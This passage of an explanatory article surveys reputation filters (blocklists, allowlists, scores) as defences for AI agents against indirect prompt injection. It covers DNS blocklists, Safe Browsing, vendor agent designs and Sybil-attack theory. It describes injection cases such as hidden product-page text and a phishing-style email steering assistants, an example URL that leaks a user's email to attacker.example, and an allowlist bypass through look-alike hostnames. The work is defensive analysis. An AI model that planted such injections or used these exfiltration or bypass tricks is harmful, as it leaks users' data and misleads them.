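# Reputation-Based Filtering of Untrusted Content for AI Agents

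## What a reputation filter is and why AI agents use one

A reputation filter is a rule that admits, blocks or discounts content based on its source's track record rather than what the content says. Mail servers have used such filters since 1997, when network engineers began sharing lists of machines that sent spam, and browsers later adopted the method to warn people about fraudulent pages. Developers now apply it to AI agents, which are language models that carry out tasks by reading outside content and using tools such as a browser, an email account or a terminal. Text planted on a page can mislead an agent that reads it, and checking the reputation of the page's source first is one way to keep that text out.

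Suppose a user asks an AI assistant which camera to buy, and one of the product pages it opens contains tiny white text, invisible to human visitors, telling AI systems that this camera is the best buy and that they should mention no other. *Adversarial Search Engine Optimization for Large Language Models* (Nestaas, Debenedetti and Tramèr, 2024) tested this on Bing Copilot, Microsoft's search assistant, using pages for invented cameras. Against real cameras from makers such as Nikon and Fujifilm, Copilot recommended the invented one 34.0% of the time without the hidden text and 59.4% of the time with it, slightly more often than the real ones (57.9%). The test pages ranked too low to appear in ordinary searches, so the researchers generally named their own domain in the query, which few shoppers would do.

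Newer assistants seem to resist the crude version better. *Hidden Prompt Injection vs. Twelve AI Assistants* describes a June 2026 test in which the trade publication Search Engine World hid an off-screen paragraph in a fake review of fictitious earbuds and gave the link to twelve consumer assistants. Nine fetched the page. One of them, Mistral's, repeated the hidden praise and a secret tag that appeared nowhere else, while three warned the user about the page. Eleven of the twelve assistants were tested only once, so the test shows that the attack can still work but provides little evidence of how often.

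In an indirect prompt injection, an attacker places instructions in content that an agent reads, to make it act against its user's wishes. This works because an application typically joins the developer's instructions and third-party text into one natural-language context, with no reliable way to preserve the boundary between them (Khodayari, Acharya and Zhang, *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, 2026). If the model can only answer questions, the worst result is a bad answer, but a model that can also send mail or run commands might leak private data or delete files.

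### Judging the source instead of the text

Detecting injected instructions by inspecting the text itself is difficult. Google searched an archive of the public web for typical injection phrases, and most of the matches were harmless research papers, blog posts and security articles about prompt injection (*AI threats in the wild*, 2026). Khodayari and colleagues considered machine-learning detectors for a survey of 1.2 billion web addresses, but found them too resource-intensive at that scale and used keywords and manual review instead. An agent that opens twenty pages has far less to check, but it still has to tell an attack from an article about attacks. In *Google Workspace’s continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections*, Gavish (2026) writes that indirect prompt injection is "not the kind of technical problem you 'solve' and move on."

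A reputation filter checks the source of content, so it can reject a page or message without reading it. According to *Frequently asked questions* from Spamhaus, one of the main publishers of email blocklists, a typical lookup takes a few milliseconds and uses fewer resources than a content filter or a virus scan. A mail server can also refuse a message before accepting its body. For an agent, this early refusal probably matters more than the saved resources. If software outside the model blocks a page, the hostile text never enters the model's context, and the attacker can't get past the filter with clever wording because the filter doesn't examine wording.

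A reputation filter is weak because a source's record is useful only so far as it predicts what the source is serving now. Sometimes it should predict this well. Infosecurity Magazine's *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents* reports two live campaigns in which attackers set up impostor sites, one posing as software documentation and the other as a cryptocurrency service, and pushed them up the search results. Once a blocklist includes such a site, the agent can't reach any of its pages. But attackers can also put text on reputable sites. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (2025) works through the case of an assistant that summarises customer reviews from an online store. An attacker only has to write a review to put hostile text on the pages of a store with a good record.

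Reputation filters also don't address some kinds of influence, such as ordinary sales language. In *A Cue's Hidden Price*, Buecheler, Berbeglia and Guo (2026) had language models choose between matched products, one of which carried an extra sentence or a more flattering phrasing of the same facts. They raised that product's price until the models picked it only half the time. With each of six such cues, the models chose the product at least 95% of the time at equal prices, but the price premium that cancelled the cue ranged from 1.6% to 21.4%. Ordinary sellers use lines like "Chosen by over 1,000 customers", and a list of bad sources has no reason to include those sellers.

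### Blocklists, allowlists and scores

A blocklist names sources to refuse and lets in everything else. An allowlist names sources to admit, and the filter refuses the rest or asks for approval. In practice, they differ in how they treat a source that nobody has judged yet. An attacker can get past a blocklist by using a site with no record, but getting past an allowlist requires putting text on a site that is already listed. An allowlist can also keep out useful sources, such as a small specialist shop that would help an agent compare cameras but that nobody thought to add.

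A reputation filter can give a source a numerical score instead of a verdict. *An Architecture for Reputation Reporting* (Borenstein and Kucherawy, 2013) defines reputation as "the estimation in which an identifiable actor is held". Its scheme, an Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF) standard, pairs an assertion about the source, such as that it sends spam, with a rating from 0.0 (no support for the assertion) to 1.0 (full agreement). The IETF's *A Media Type for Reputation Interchange* adds a field for who did the rating and an optional one for the rater's confidence. The receiver then sets a threshold or combines the score with other evidence.

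An agent can also use a score to give a source's content less weight in its answer instead of blocking it. This source weighting penalizes unknown sites less than blocking does, but it loses the main benefit of filtering by source, which is keeping the text from reaching the model.

Mail servers commonly combine blocklists and allowlists. *DNS Blacklists and Whitelists* (Levine, 2010) describes a pattern in which a server checks its lists in turn, rejecting the connection at the first blocklist match and accepting it at the first allowlist match. If the sender is on no list, as is usual for legitimate mail, the server accepts the connection.

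### What an entry names

A reputation has to attach to something, such as an IP address (the number that identifies a machine on the network), a domain, a single web address, an account or a publisher. An attacker should not be able to fake it. Anyone can type a false name into the "From" line of an email, so mail systems now attach cryptographic signatures that tie a message to a domain. A signature shows who sent a message but not whether the sender is trustworthy. Borenstein and Kucherawy note that bad actors tended to adopt signing faster than good ones, hoping receivers would mistake a signed message for a trustworthy one.

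How much an entry covers matters as much as its kind. Some lists block a whole range of IP addresses on evidence from a few of them, which also blocks mail from innocent senders in the range. *Overview of Best Email DNS-Based List (DNSBL) Operational Practices* (Lewis and Sergeant, 2012) discusses this problem, usually called "collateral damage". Domain entries can cause it too. *Hostnames coming to Spamhaus Domain Blocklist (DBL) for increased accuracy* (Miller, 2021) gives the example of the website builder Wix, whose free sites are all under wixsite.com. Listing that domain because a criminal hacked one site would block every free Wix site. To avoid this, Spamhaus has since February 2022 offered entries for hacked sites that give the full hostname, which identifies a single customer's site.

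Listing a single page spares even more bystanders but gives the least protection, because an attacker who controls a site can publish the same text at a new path within seconds.

Google Safe Browsing, the service behind the warnings in the Chrome browser, checks each web address at several levels at once, from a single page to a whole domain. Google's *URLs and Hashing* describes how the browser turns an address into up to 30 strings by combining up to five versions of the host with up to six of the path. The address http://a.b.com/1/2.html?param=1 yields eight, including the exact page, the folder a.b.com/1/, the host a.b.com/ and the parent domain b.com/. A match on any of them marks the page as unsafe. None of these levels suits the planted review, because the filter would need to list the reviewer's account, which the web address may not reveal.

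### The life of an entry

List operators gather evidence for an entry by watching spamtraps, which are unpublished email addresses that, in theory, only a spammer would write to. Spamhaus runs automated tools over traffic at its traps and at working mail servers to find patterns that indicate infected machines. The nearest counterpart for web pages is a crawler, but a hostile site can show the crawler a clean page and victims the real one, which is called cloaking.

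If the evidence meets the list's criteria, the operator adds the source, ideally records why, and publishes the updated list to the servers that answer queries. Receivers look sources up and store each answer for a period the operator sets. Levine suggests that receivers might store answers about stable address ranges for several days, while a list of machines caught sending spam might change every few minutes.

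Entries should also expire. Abusix, another list operator, keeps an address on its list of compromised machines for about 5.2 days after last seeing traffic from it. Old entries are risky because addresses change hands, and in Lewis and Sergeant's experience some automated lists make more errors as time passes since the last detection. An owner can usually ask for removal sooner, and if the list detects abuse quickly, its operator can agree at once with little risk because the list will catch any new abuse.

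### One DNS lookup, step by step

Most email blocklists are published through the domain name system (DNS), the internet's directory for turning names into numbers. These are called DNS blocklists, or DNSBLs. Suppose a machine at 192.0.2.99 connects to a mail server that uses a list whose zone, its own branch of the directory, is bad.example.com. In Levine's example, the lookup works as follows.

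1. The server reverses the four parts of the address, giving 99.2.0.192. Domain names run from the particular to the general and IP addresses run the other way, so the reversal makes them fit.
2. It appends the list's zone, giving 99.2.0.192.bad.example.com.
3. It asks the DNS for the address record of that name, as if it were looking up a website.
4. If the answer is 127.0.0.2, the list contains the sender. If the answer is "no such domain", it does not.

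The number 127.0.0.2 is a code. It comes from a block of addresses that computers reserve for connections to themselves, so a program that mistakes it for a real address does no harm to anyone else. Different codes can give different reasons for a listing. If 127.0.0.2 stands for one sublist and 127.0.0.4 for another, an address on both returns 127.0.0.6, which combines the two codes bit by bit. Spamhaus returns 127.0.1.4 for a phishing domain and 127.0.1.104 for a legitimate domain that phishers are abusing, so a receiver can treat the two differently. To check a domain such as invalid.edu against a list of domains, the server puts the name in front of the zone without reversing it.

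In 2010, Levine specified that a client must treat any returned address record as a listing. Spamhaus now also uses these records for error messages, such as 127.255.255.254 when a query arrives through a public DNS server. An agent that follows the 2010 rule would treat that error as a listing and block every source it checked. The usual safeguard is to query two test addresses, because a working list always contains 127.0.0.2 and never contains 127.0.0.1.

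### Checking a page without revealing it

A DNS lookup reveals to the list's operator whom the client is dealing with. If an agent checked every page this way, the operator would build up a fairly complete record of what the user had the agent do. Safe Browsing limits this exposure by using fragments of hashes. A hash function turns any text into a fixed-length number, here 32 bytes, that nobody can practically turn back into the text.

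The browser hashes each string it has made from the address and keeps only the first four bytes of each hash, called the prefix. In the procedure in Google's *Local List Mode*, it compares these prefixes with a downloaded list of hash prefixes for unsafe addresses. If nothing matches, the browser treats the page as safe and Google learns nothing. If a prefix matches, the browser sends it to Google, receives the full unsafe-address hashes that begin with it, and makes the final comparison on the user's device.

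The short prefix protects the user's privacy. A four-byte prefix has 2^32 possible values, about 4.3 billion. If the web held a trillion addresses, about 230 of them would share each prefix on average, and Google could not tell which one the user was visiting. Two matching prefixes from the same page would narrow the possibilities considerably. Short prefixes also produce chance matches. With a million entries on the list, a harmless page with 30 strings would match about 0.7% of the time. Comparing the full hashes rules out these matches. If the request to Google fails, the procedure returns "safe", which is reasonable for a person who wants the web to keep working but more debatable for an unsupervised agent.

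But downloaded lists go out of date. Chrome refreshed its copy every 30 to 60 minutes, while most unsafe sites existed for less than ten minutes, according to Google's *Real-time, privacy-preserving URL protection* (2024). Chrome now checks with the server whenever a page is not on a stored list of safe ones. It sends the encrypted prefixes through a relay run by another company, Fastly. Fastly can see the user's IP address but not the prefixes, and Google can see the prefixes but not the IP address. According to Google's *Overview* of the service, developers can instead choose a simpler method that sends the full web address. An agent that uses this method loses the privacy protection.

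### From spam lists to browsers

Reputation filtering began in 1997, when the internet engineers Dave Rand and Paul Vixie started a list of IP addresses that had sent them spam. They first distributed it as a feed that routers could use to drop all traffic from those addresses, and it became known as the Real-time Blackhole List. Many network managers wanted to block only the mail, so Rand and Vixie created a DNS version. Spammers responded by relaying their messages through other people's badly secured servers, and other volunteers built lists to catch that. By 2012, Lewis and Sergeant put the number of public lists at more than 700. Some of these listed the domains in links inside a message, regardless of who had sent it. Google Safe Browsing, more than 15 years old by 2024, and Microsoft's SmartScreen brought source checks to the browser, where they help determine whether to open a page.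 An agent's filter has to make the same decision.

All of these systems can fail in similar ways. A filter can miss a hostile source that nobody has reported yet, or block a harmless one that shares an address or domain with a hostile one. Attackers can switch to a new source once the old one is listed, which is called source rotation. They can also poison a list by submitting false evidence, so that it blocks a rival or clears a malicious site. A list's owner also has power over everyone who relies on it. Some operators have listed the entire internet when they shut down, so mail servers still using the list rejected all mail.

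There are very different kinds of evidence on these failures. Product documents describe what a check was built to do, but seldom how often it succeeds. Theory can show that some schemes must fail if creating a new identity takes no money or effort, but only measurement can establish how much it takes in practice. The large measurements concern spam and phishing, which target people, and pages written for agents may last longer or attract fewer reports. Experiments can isolate a cause, as Nestaas and colleagues did by changing one hidden line, but they usually use invented pages and models that companies soon replace. A case report of a poisoned list or a wrongful block proves that such a failure has happened, but not how often it happens, because people write up the striking cases. Court records offer contested and documented facts about single disputes under one country's law. Comparisons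 of the institutions that run shared lists can show which arrangements have lasted, but not whether they would suit software that opens pages on its own.

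## How current agent products judge sources

When an agent opens a web page, it both receives and sends information. The page's text enters the model's context, where planted instructions can mislead it, and the page's address goes to the site's server, where an attacker can read any data the agent has included in the address. An inbound filter controls what the agent may read, and an outbound filter controls where it may send data. A site can be safe to read but dangerous to send data to. For example, a file-sharing service may publish harmless help pages, but an attacker who controls the agent could make it upload a user's documents to the attacker's account there.

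OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) explains that an attack usually needs both a way to influence the agent and an action that does harm, such as sending information to a third party. Blocking either one is enough to stop such an attack, so an outbound filter can still protect a user whose agent has read something hostile.

Most of what outsiders know about these filters comes from the companies that build them. Microsoft, Anthropic, OpenAI and Google explain what their checks do and what happens when a page fails one. In the same documents, they give no figures for how many hostile pages the checks catch or how many harmless ones they block. They also say little about how a site gets onto a list.

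### Microsoft Edge

In October 2025, Microsoft released a preview of a Copilot agent in its Edge browser that clicks, types and moves between pages for the user. According to Microsoft's *Considerations for Safe Agentic Browsing* (2025), the agent could by default act only on sites on a curated list and any others the user approved. A stricter setting ignored the curated list and asked the user about every site. In addition, SmartScreen blocked sites confirmed as phishing, malware or scams, and the agent could not click past its block page.

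Microsoft also kept a blocklist of sites "unsafe for Copilot to read", which it said it could update within hours. SmartScreen could block a newly confirmed scam site within minutes. Both times are counted from when Microsoft identifies the site, so they exclude the time it takes to discover the attack, which may be longer.

The consumer rules now look different. Microsoft's current help page for the feature, Browse with Copilot, mentions no curated list. It describes blocklists for high-risk sites, such as adult content and gambling, and says Copilot may ask for approval if a site seems unrelated to the task. The forum guide *Allow or Block Sites for Browse with Copilot in Microsoft Edge* shows that users can also keep their own lists of allowed and blocked sites. Microsoft seems to have moved from an allowlist towards a blocklist, which would let the agent use far more of the web, although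 the help page might simply omit the default. The two example categories also have little to do with prompt injection. Hidden instructions for a shopping agent are more likely to appear on a fake review site than on a gambling site.

Businesses get more control. Microsoft's *Edge for Business presents* (2025) says that administrators had to supply a list of approved sites before the agent would work, and recommends starting with a short one. Administrators can now also switch on a ready-made list of "commonly used sites for work", according to Microsoft's *Configure browsing with Copilot*. Microsoft's *Browsing with Copilot Blocked URLs* describes a policy, available from version 148 of Edge, that lets a company allow every site except those it blocks. Two companies with the same browser can therefore have very different protection.

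### Lists of bad sites and lists of busy ones

Eric Lawrence, who works on SmartScreen, doubts that either kind of list is enough. In *AI Injection Attacks*, a post on his personal blog, he writes that agents should be kept away from known bad sites but that this is "wildly insufficient", because new bad sites appear all the time and SmartScreen looks for phishing, malware and tech-support scams. He thinks it very unlikely that anyone today would even recognise a site carrying out prompt injection.

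The second reason seems more serious for agents, because faster updates would help with new scam sites but not with attacks that the list-maker isn't looking for. A page with hidden instructions for an agent may not ask visitors for a password or install anything on their computers, so human visitors have no reason to report it. Microsoft's separate blocklist for Copilot partly addresses this because it can list a site for what the site does to an agent, but somebody still has to notice the attack before the site is listed.

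Allowing only good sites is also difficult, because nobody has a list of them. Lawrence writes that the closest thing SmartScreen has is a list of high-traffic sites that are unlikely to host the particular threats it covers. Busy sites are poor targets for blocking because a mistake would affect many people, but high traffic is little evidence that an agent should believe what it finds there. Microsoft's ready-made list for businesses also describes its sites by how commonly people use them. Many good sites also carry comments, advertisements and snippets from elsewhere, so they are open to the same trick as the planted store review.

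Lawrence gives no figures, and his argument doesn't show that allowlists are useless. Getting text onto an approved site is still harder than registering a new domain, especially if the site moderates what visitors post, but it would take experiments to find out how much harder.

He also considers limiting what the agent can do instead of what it reads. A company could require constant human approval, or run the agent on an isolated machine without the user's data or passwords. These limits would reduce the damage a hijacked agent could do to very little, but they would also prevent the agent from booking a restaurant, ordering flowers and emailing a reminder to the user's wife, his example of what people want. As long as companies compete to offer agents that do such things, they will need to control what those agents read and where the agents send data.

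### Claude Code's web fetch

Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, reads web pages through a tool called WebFetch. Anthropic's documentation describes the rules, and Shilkov (2025), in *Inside Claude Code's Web Tools*, worked out some undocumented details by watching the program run. A fetch works roughly as follows.

1. Claude Code compares the site's hostname with the user's rules. Rules that deny access come first, then rules that require a question, then rules that allow access. A built-in set of software documentation sites needs no approval unless the user has made a rule to the contrary.
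2. If no rule settles the matter, Claude Code asks the user or, in a setting called auto mode, has a classifier review the fetch.
3. Before fetching, it also sends the hostname to an Anthropic service, which answers whether the fetch may go ahead. This happens even for sites the user has allowed, although a setting can turn it off.
4. It downloads the page. If the address redirects to a different host, the tool stops and reports the new address. The agent then has to make a second request, which goes through the same checks.
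5. A smaller model reads the page and answers a question about it. The main model usually receives only that answer.

According to Anthropic's documentation, sessions in a terminal or the VS Code editor now start in auto mode by default, so a classifier makes decisions that the agent used to stop and ask the user about. This avoids teaching people to approve everything, but the protection now depends on the classifier's accuracy.

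Shilkov found that the service in step 3 receives a hostname and returns a yes or no. He guessed that it keeps a list of malicious domains and may also consider copyright and robots.txt, the file that lists what automated visitors should not access on a site, but he called the exact rules "opaque". A refusal therefore doesn't necessarily mean that a site is dangerous. And because the service receives only the hostname, it has to return the same answer for every project on a code-hosting site, including one that an attacker has just uploaded.

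The smaller model provides some protection after the source check. Shilkov suggests that an attacker would have to trick it and then trick the main model through its summary. He calls this speculation and says the arrangement is not bulletproof.

The rules also cover only the WebFetch tool. If Claude Code is allowed to run shell commands outside a sandbox (an isolated environment that restricts what commands can reach), it can download any page with a program such as curl. Anthropic states this on its permissions page and recommends combining WebFetch rules with the sandbox's network allowlist.

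The sandbox shows why inbound and outbound permission should be separate. According to Anthropic's documentation from September 2026, commands in the sandbox do not inherit the built-in set of documentation sites. This is sensible because a shell command that can reach a site may be able to upload files to it. But if a user chooses "don't ask again" for a site, Claude Code saves a rule for that domain, and the rule normally lets sandboxed commands reach the site too. A user who only wanted the agent to read a page has then also given it a way to send data out.

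### A correct list with a faulty match

An allowlist also depends on how the program compares addresses with its entries. NIST's *CVE-2026-24052 Detail*, an entry in the US government's database of software flaws, describes an error in how Claude Code did this. Before version 1.0.111, Claude Code accepted any address that began with a trusted name, such as docs.python.org or modelcontextprotocol.io. But whoever owns example.com can create any name ending in .example.com, including modelcontextprotocol.io.example.com, which begins with a trusted name and belongs to someone else.

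With such a name, an attacker could have received requests that Claude Code sent without the user's consent, including any private data in the address. The attack would have worked even if every entry on the list was trustworthy. The entry for this flaw rates its severity as high, at 7.1 out of 10, and describes what attackers could have done but reports no actual attack. According to GitLab (2026), users with automatic updates already had the fix when the flaw became public in February 2026.

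The current rules are much stricter, as these examples from Anthropic's documentation show.

| Rule for a domain | Matches | Does not match |
|---|---|---|
| example.com | example.com | api.example.com |
| *.example.com | api.example.com and a.b.example.com | example.com |
| example.* | example.org | example.evil.com |

The asterisk in the last row can stand for only one part of the name, between two dots. If it could stand for more, the owner of evil.com could create a matching name, which would bring back the old flaw.

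Rules that match the text of a command are even weaker. Anthropic gives the example of a rule meant to restrict curl to GitHub addresses. The rule fails to recognise the same request if the command puts an option before the address, uses https instead of http, or stores the address in a variable. A program must check the actual destination to control where data goes, and a redirect can change that destination after the check.

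### OpenAI's exact-address check

OpenAI designed ChatGPT's main link check to keep user data from leaking through URLs. Suppose a hostile page gets the agent to open https://attacker.example/collect?data= followed by the user's email address. Websites commonly log requested URLs, so the attacker can read the email address in the log even if the agent never mentions it in the chat. The same leak can happen when the agent loads an image in the background, which the user may not notice.

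OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) gives two objections to letting an agent open only well-known sites. First, many legitimate sites have links that forward visitors elsewhere, so a check that looks only at the first domain can approve a request that ends up on an attacker's server. Claude Code deals with this by stopping whenever a link forwards it to a new host. Second, people use far more than a handful of top sites, so a strict list would produce frequent false alarms and train them to click through warnings without thinking.

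OpenAI therefore switched to checking whether the exact URL has already appeared on the public web, independently of any user's conversation with ChatGPT, rather than whether the site is reputable. The check has four steps.

1. A crawler collects addresses from public pages, as a search engine does. It has no access to conversations, accounts or personal data.
2. Before the agent opens an address automatically, the system looks for that exact address in the crawler's index.
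3. If the address is there, the agent can load it.
4. If it isn't, the system either tells the agent to try another site or warns the user that the link may contain information from the conversation.

The check works because the crawler can't have seen a secret that exists only in the user's conversation. If an attacker gets the agent to add that secret to a URL, the URL will almost certainly be new, and the lookup will fail. The domain's reputation doesn't affect the result, so the check also catches private data added to a redirect link on a well-known site.

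The security blog Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* points out that an attacker with many pages in the index can still learn something from which of them the agent opens. Opening one of 1,000 pages reveals at most about ten bits, roughly two random letters, so a long secret would take many requests. The blog suggests making this harder by stopping the agent from opening the same address repeatedly in one session. It also notes that an address typed by the user counts as safe for that session.

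OpenAI acknowledges that this design does not ensure that a page is honest, and that a page that passes may still contain misleading or harmful instructions. An attacker's page can pass as soon as the crawler has recorded its address. The index records which addresses exist but does not assess how their owners have behaved, so it does very little to filter what the agent reads.

 

The check may not end warning fatigue either. A page published an hour ago, a private sharing link or an unusual search query may be missing from the index for innocent reasons. OpenAI doesn't say how often users see the warning. Sending the agent to another site avoids an interruption, but the user may never learn that the agent skipped the best source.

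A company's check may also cover only some of its products. Embrace The Red reports that OpenAI introduced a first version of its check in December 2023 but left it out of some products, including its macOS and iOS apps. OpenAI says that by March 2026 the newer check also covered page visits in its Atlas browser and in Deep Research, its research agent.

OpenAI puts this much effort into the outbound side because it doesn't expect to recognise every incoming attack. Its March post describes an email that posed as a follow-up about company restructuring and told the assistant it was authorised to submit an employee's details to a "compliance validation system". The attack worked 50% of the time in testing with one user request. OpenAI argues that spotting such a message is as hard as spotting a lie, often without the necessary context.

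Willison (2026) describes a similar leak in Claude, where an attack extracted a user's name, home city and employer through the web-fetching tool. Anthropic closed it with a blunter fix, stopping the tool from following links found inside pages it had fetched. This prevents a hostile page from directing the tool to another address, but it also prevents the tool from following a useful page's links to its sources.

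### Relevance to the task in Chrome

Google's agent in Chrome judges a site mainly by whether it is relevant to the user's task. *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) describes a design that sorts origins (roughly, individual sites) into two sets for each session. The agent may only read from origins in the first set, but may also act on those in the second, for example by clicking and typing. A separate component assigns origins to the sets without seeing untrusted web content, so a hostile page can't use its content to get itself added. The browser hides from the model any part of a page that comes from an origin outside both sets, such as an embedded advertisement.

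In this design, the readable set limits what can influence the agent, and the writable set limits where the agent can pass on what it has learned. But the first version tracked only the writable set, so the restriction on reading was still only planned in December 2025. Berschadski (2026), in *Future Mode Part 2*, says that Chrome limits the agent to origins "strictly relevant to the immediate task", but doesn't say whether the separate readable set is now in use.

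Chrome also uses lists, for narrower purposes. Safe Browsing still checks for conventional threats, and addresses that the model generates must be known and public, much as in OpenAI's design. Another list names sensitive sites, such as those for banking or medical records, which the agent can visit only after the user confirms. Sites are on this list because a hijacked agent could do a lot of harm there, even if the sites themselves are trustworthy.

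Relevance and reputation checks can give opposite results. Microsoft's October 2025 post shows Edge's relevance check pausing because Wikipedia may be unrelated to the task, although few people would blocklist Wikipedia. A fake camera page, however, is relevant to a user who wants to buy a camera. A relevance check could stop that page from sending the agent to the user's bank, but it would not stop the agent from reading the page and recommending the camera.

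## What theory says when new identities are cheap

Once the fake camera page is on a blocklist, its owner can move it to a new domain with no record. A bad reputation hurts only someone who has to keep the same name or pay for a new one. Economists and computer scientists studied this problem in online auctions and file-sharing networks long before AI agents browsed the web, and much of what they found also applies to agents.

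### Why honest newcomers pay

In *The Social Cost of Cheap Pseudonyms*, Friedman and Resnick (2001) modelled an online community as a repeated game. In each period, members meet in random pairs, and each either cooperates or cheats. If both cooperate, each gets 1 point. A member who cheats a cooperator gets 2 points and the victim loses 1. If both cheat, both get 0. After each period, a share α of the members leaves and the same number of new people join, so the average member stays for 1/α periods. Everyone can see each name's history, but anyone can take a new name for free between periods, and nobody can tell a renamed cheat from a real newcomer.

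If names were permanent, members could cooperate with everyone except those who broke the rules in the previous period. A cheat would gain 1 point now and lose 2 in the next period, ending up worse off. If new names are free, a cheat can avoid the punishment by returning as a newcomer. Members could instead agree to stop cooperating forever after anyone cheats once. This would deter cheats without mistreating newcomers, but one vandal or one mistyped key would end all cooperation. To rule out such fragile arrangements, Friedman and Resnick gave each member a small chance of doing the opposite of what they intended.

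One arrangement that survives these errors is to make newcomers pay dues. A newcomer cooperates with an established member, who cheats the newcomer in a fraction q of the periods. To see how large q must be, ignore the rare errors and assume a large community. A cheat gains 1 point and, with probability 1 − α, is still around in the next period to pay for it as a newcomer. If the next partner is an established member, the dues cost the cheat 2 points (−1 instead of 1). If the partner is another newcomer, the cheat misses the 1 extra point that an established member would have collected. The average loss when dues apply is 2(1 − α) + α, or 2 − α, so cheating doesn't pay if

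q · (1 − α) · (2 − α) ≥ 1.

If a tenth of the members leave each period, q must be at least 0.58, so established members have to mistreat honest newcomers more than half the time because a few newcomers might be cheats.

When a newcomer pays dues, the newcomer loses 2 points and the established member gains 1, so the community loses 1. If a fraction α of the members leave each period, the average payoff per period is 1 − α/(2 − α), compared with 1 under permanent names. The loss is about 5% if a tenth of the members leave each period and 14% if a quarter do. Friedman and Resnick proved that no stable arrangement can do noticeably better, provided that α is below 0.3, the community is large, and errors are rare but do happen.

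For an agent, the newcomers are new domains, which lose visits when a filter blocks or discounts them. The overall loss may be greater than in the game, where established members get half of what newcomers lose. If an agent skips a new specialist shop, the shop loses a customer and the user may miss the best camera. In the game, everyone also sees every act of cheating. A user whose agent obeyed a hidden instruction may never find out, so a hostile site could keep a clean record without changing its name.

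Charging for each name would let members trust newcomers, but a single price rarely suits everyone. Friedman and Resnick give an example in which members stay for ten periods on average, so the game is worth at most 10 points to each of them, and a unit of money is worth 1 point to poor members but only 0.01 points to rich ones. A fee must exceed 100 units to outweigh a rich member's 1-point gain from cheating. Poor members would lose more than 100 points by paying it, so they stay out. Similarly, a domain price high enough to deter a profitable fraud business would probably drive away hobbyists first.

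They preferred to have a trusted intermediary issue each person one certificate per community. With a cryptographic method called a blind signature, the intermediary can certify a name without learning what it is, so members stay anonymous but can't start over under a new name. This restores full cooperation in the model. But someone has to check that each applicant is a different person, and on the web one person can legitimately own hundreds of domains.

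### One attacker posing as many

Friedman, Resnick and Sami (2007), in *Manipulation-Resistant Reputation Systems*, call starting over under a new name "whitewashing". They distinguish it from the Sybil attack, in which one party uses many identities at once, for example to praise itself. Whitewashing lets a source evade a blocklist, while a Sybil attack corrupts any score that depends on other people's reports, reviews or links.

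In *The Sybil Attack*, Douceur (2002) asked whether a computer can tell if two unfamiliar identities on a network belong to different parties. In his model, no authority vouches for anyone, and participants know each other only through messages. Two identities can directly prove they are distinct only by doing something a single party couldn't, such as each solving a hard computing puzzle in the same short period. He proved four limits on such checks.

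- An attacker with ten times the resources of the weakest participant can pass as ten participants.
- If the checks don't all happen at the same time, one attacker can pass as any number of participants by reusing the same resources for each check.
- If the system accepts anyone whom q accepted identities vouch for, q cooperating attackers can create any number of fakes. Fewer attackers can do it if they have enough resources.
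- If honest participants don't coordinate the timing of their checks, even the weakest attacker can get one identity for every q of them. With 1,000 honest participants and q = 10, that makes 100 identities.

Without an authority, a system can prevent Sybil attacks only if all participants have nearly equal resources, everyone checks all identities simultaneously, and the number of participants who must vouch for an identity exceeds the number of attackers. Douceur considered these conditions unrealistic in a large system. His result does not rule out preventing the attacks by having an authority establish who is who.

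Domains do have an authority, so the impossibility result doesn't strictly apply to them. Douceur observed that systems which identify machines by IP address or domain name implicitly rely on ICANN, which coordinates both. But the domain system ensures only that each name has one holder. A holder can have as many names as they can pay for, so the number of fakes depends on their price. The price can be zero for sites under a shared domain, such as wixsite.com, and for reviewer accounts on a store.

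### Which scores resist fake votes

Even if creating fake identities takes no effort, a reputation score might be designed so that they don't help. Cheng and Friedman (2005), in *Sybilproof reputation mechanisms*, investigated when this is possible. They treated a reputation system as a network in which each identity is a point and each link records how much one identity trusts another. A reputation function computes scores from this network.

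A function is symmetric if the scores depend only on the pattern of links, not on which identity is which. PageRank, Google's original method for ranking web pages by the links between them, is symmetric. Cheng and Friedman proved that no symmetric function is sybilproof, meaning that for every such function there is some case where an attacker can overtake somebody by adding fake identities. An attacker can copy the whole network using fake identities, including a double of the top-ranked member. Because the double has the same pattern of links as the original, the attacker now controls an identity with the same score. Loiseau (2016), in the lecture slides *Network Economics*, gives a stronger version that holds even if the attacker may add only one fake.

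Functions that start from a chosen, trusted point can do better. The max-flow method treats each link as a pipe whose width is the amount of trust, and a member's score is how much can flow to it from the trusted point. An attacker can't raise its own score by adding fake identities, because they can widen the pipes among themselves but not the pipes that lead in from outside. It may still overtake a rival if some of the rival's trust flows through it. The attacker can lower the rival's score by splitting into two unconnected identities, one that receives trust and one that should pass it on. According to Loiseau, another method, PathRank, prevents this too.

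An attacker can still exploit a sybilproof score if they need many identities with moderate scores rather than one with a high rank. *Achieving Sybil-Proofness in Distributed Work Systems* (Stannat, Ileri and colleagues, 2021) points out that under max-flow, many fakes can each get a moderate score, and their total has no limit. If an agent uses such scores as weights and adds them up for all the sites that recommend a camera, a hundred moderately trusted fakes could outweigh one excellent reviewer.

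In *Anduin* (2026), Ramji, Zeng and colleagues at the payments company Circle tested scores of this type on a market where AI agents buy online services. They collected 66 million payments worth $6.1 million over 157 days. Sellers there can easily fake a simple popularity ranking by paying themselves from their own accounts, losing only the transaction fees. The paper's score instead starts from the sellers a buyer already pays, then follows the payments those sellers' other customers make. An attacker can join this network only by paying real money to a seller the buyer already uses.

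In simulated attacks on 813 buyers, manipulating the new score cost 20% of those buyers' total spending, compared with 0.9% for a method that counts what similar customers bought. The score's top-ranked seller was the one the buyer chose next for 23.6% of buyers, compared with 3.7% for a ranking by popularity. The guarantee assumes that the attacker controls none of the buyer's existing sellers, so it fails if someone hacks one of them. The score also leaves sellers with no connection to the buyer's network unrated, which again puts honest newcomers at a disadvantage. Agents read most web pages without paying for them, so a web filter would need some other record that is equally expensive to fake.

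*SybilGuard* and *SybilRank*, two well-known defences against fake identities, assume that honest members are well connected to each other and have few links to the fakes, according to the review in *Manipulation-resistant reputation for peer-to-peer scientific publishing* (2026). Links are a poor defence on the web, because an attacker can get them from honest sites by posting comments or hacking pages.

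Cheng and Friedman's theorem covers scores that a system computes from what its members report about each other. It doesn't apply to a list operator that gathers its own evidence, for example with spamtraps or a crawler. Such an operator can ignore fake votes, but it still has to find each new hostile source after the attacker starts using it.

### When switching sources pays

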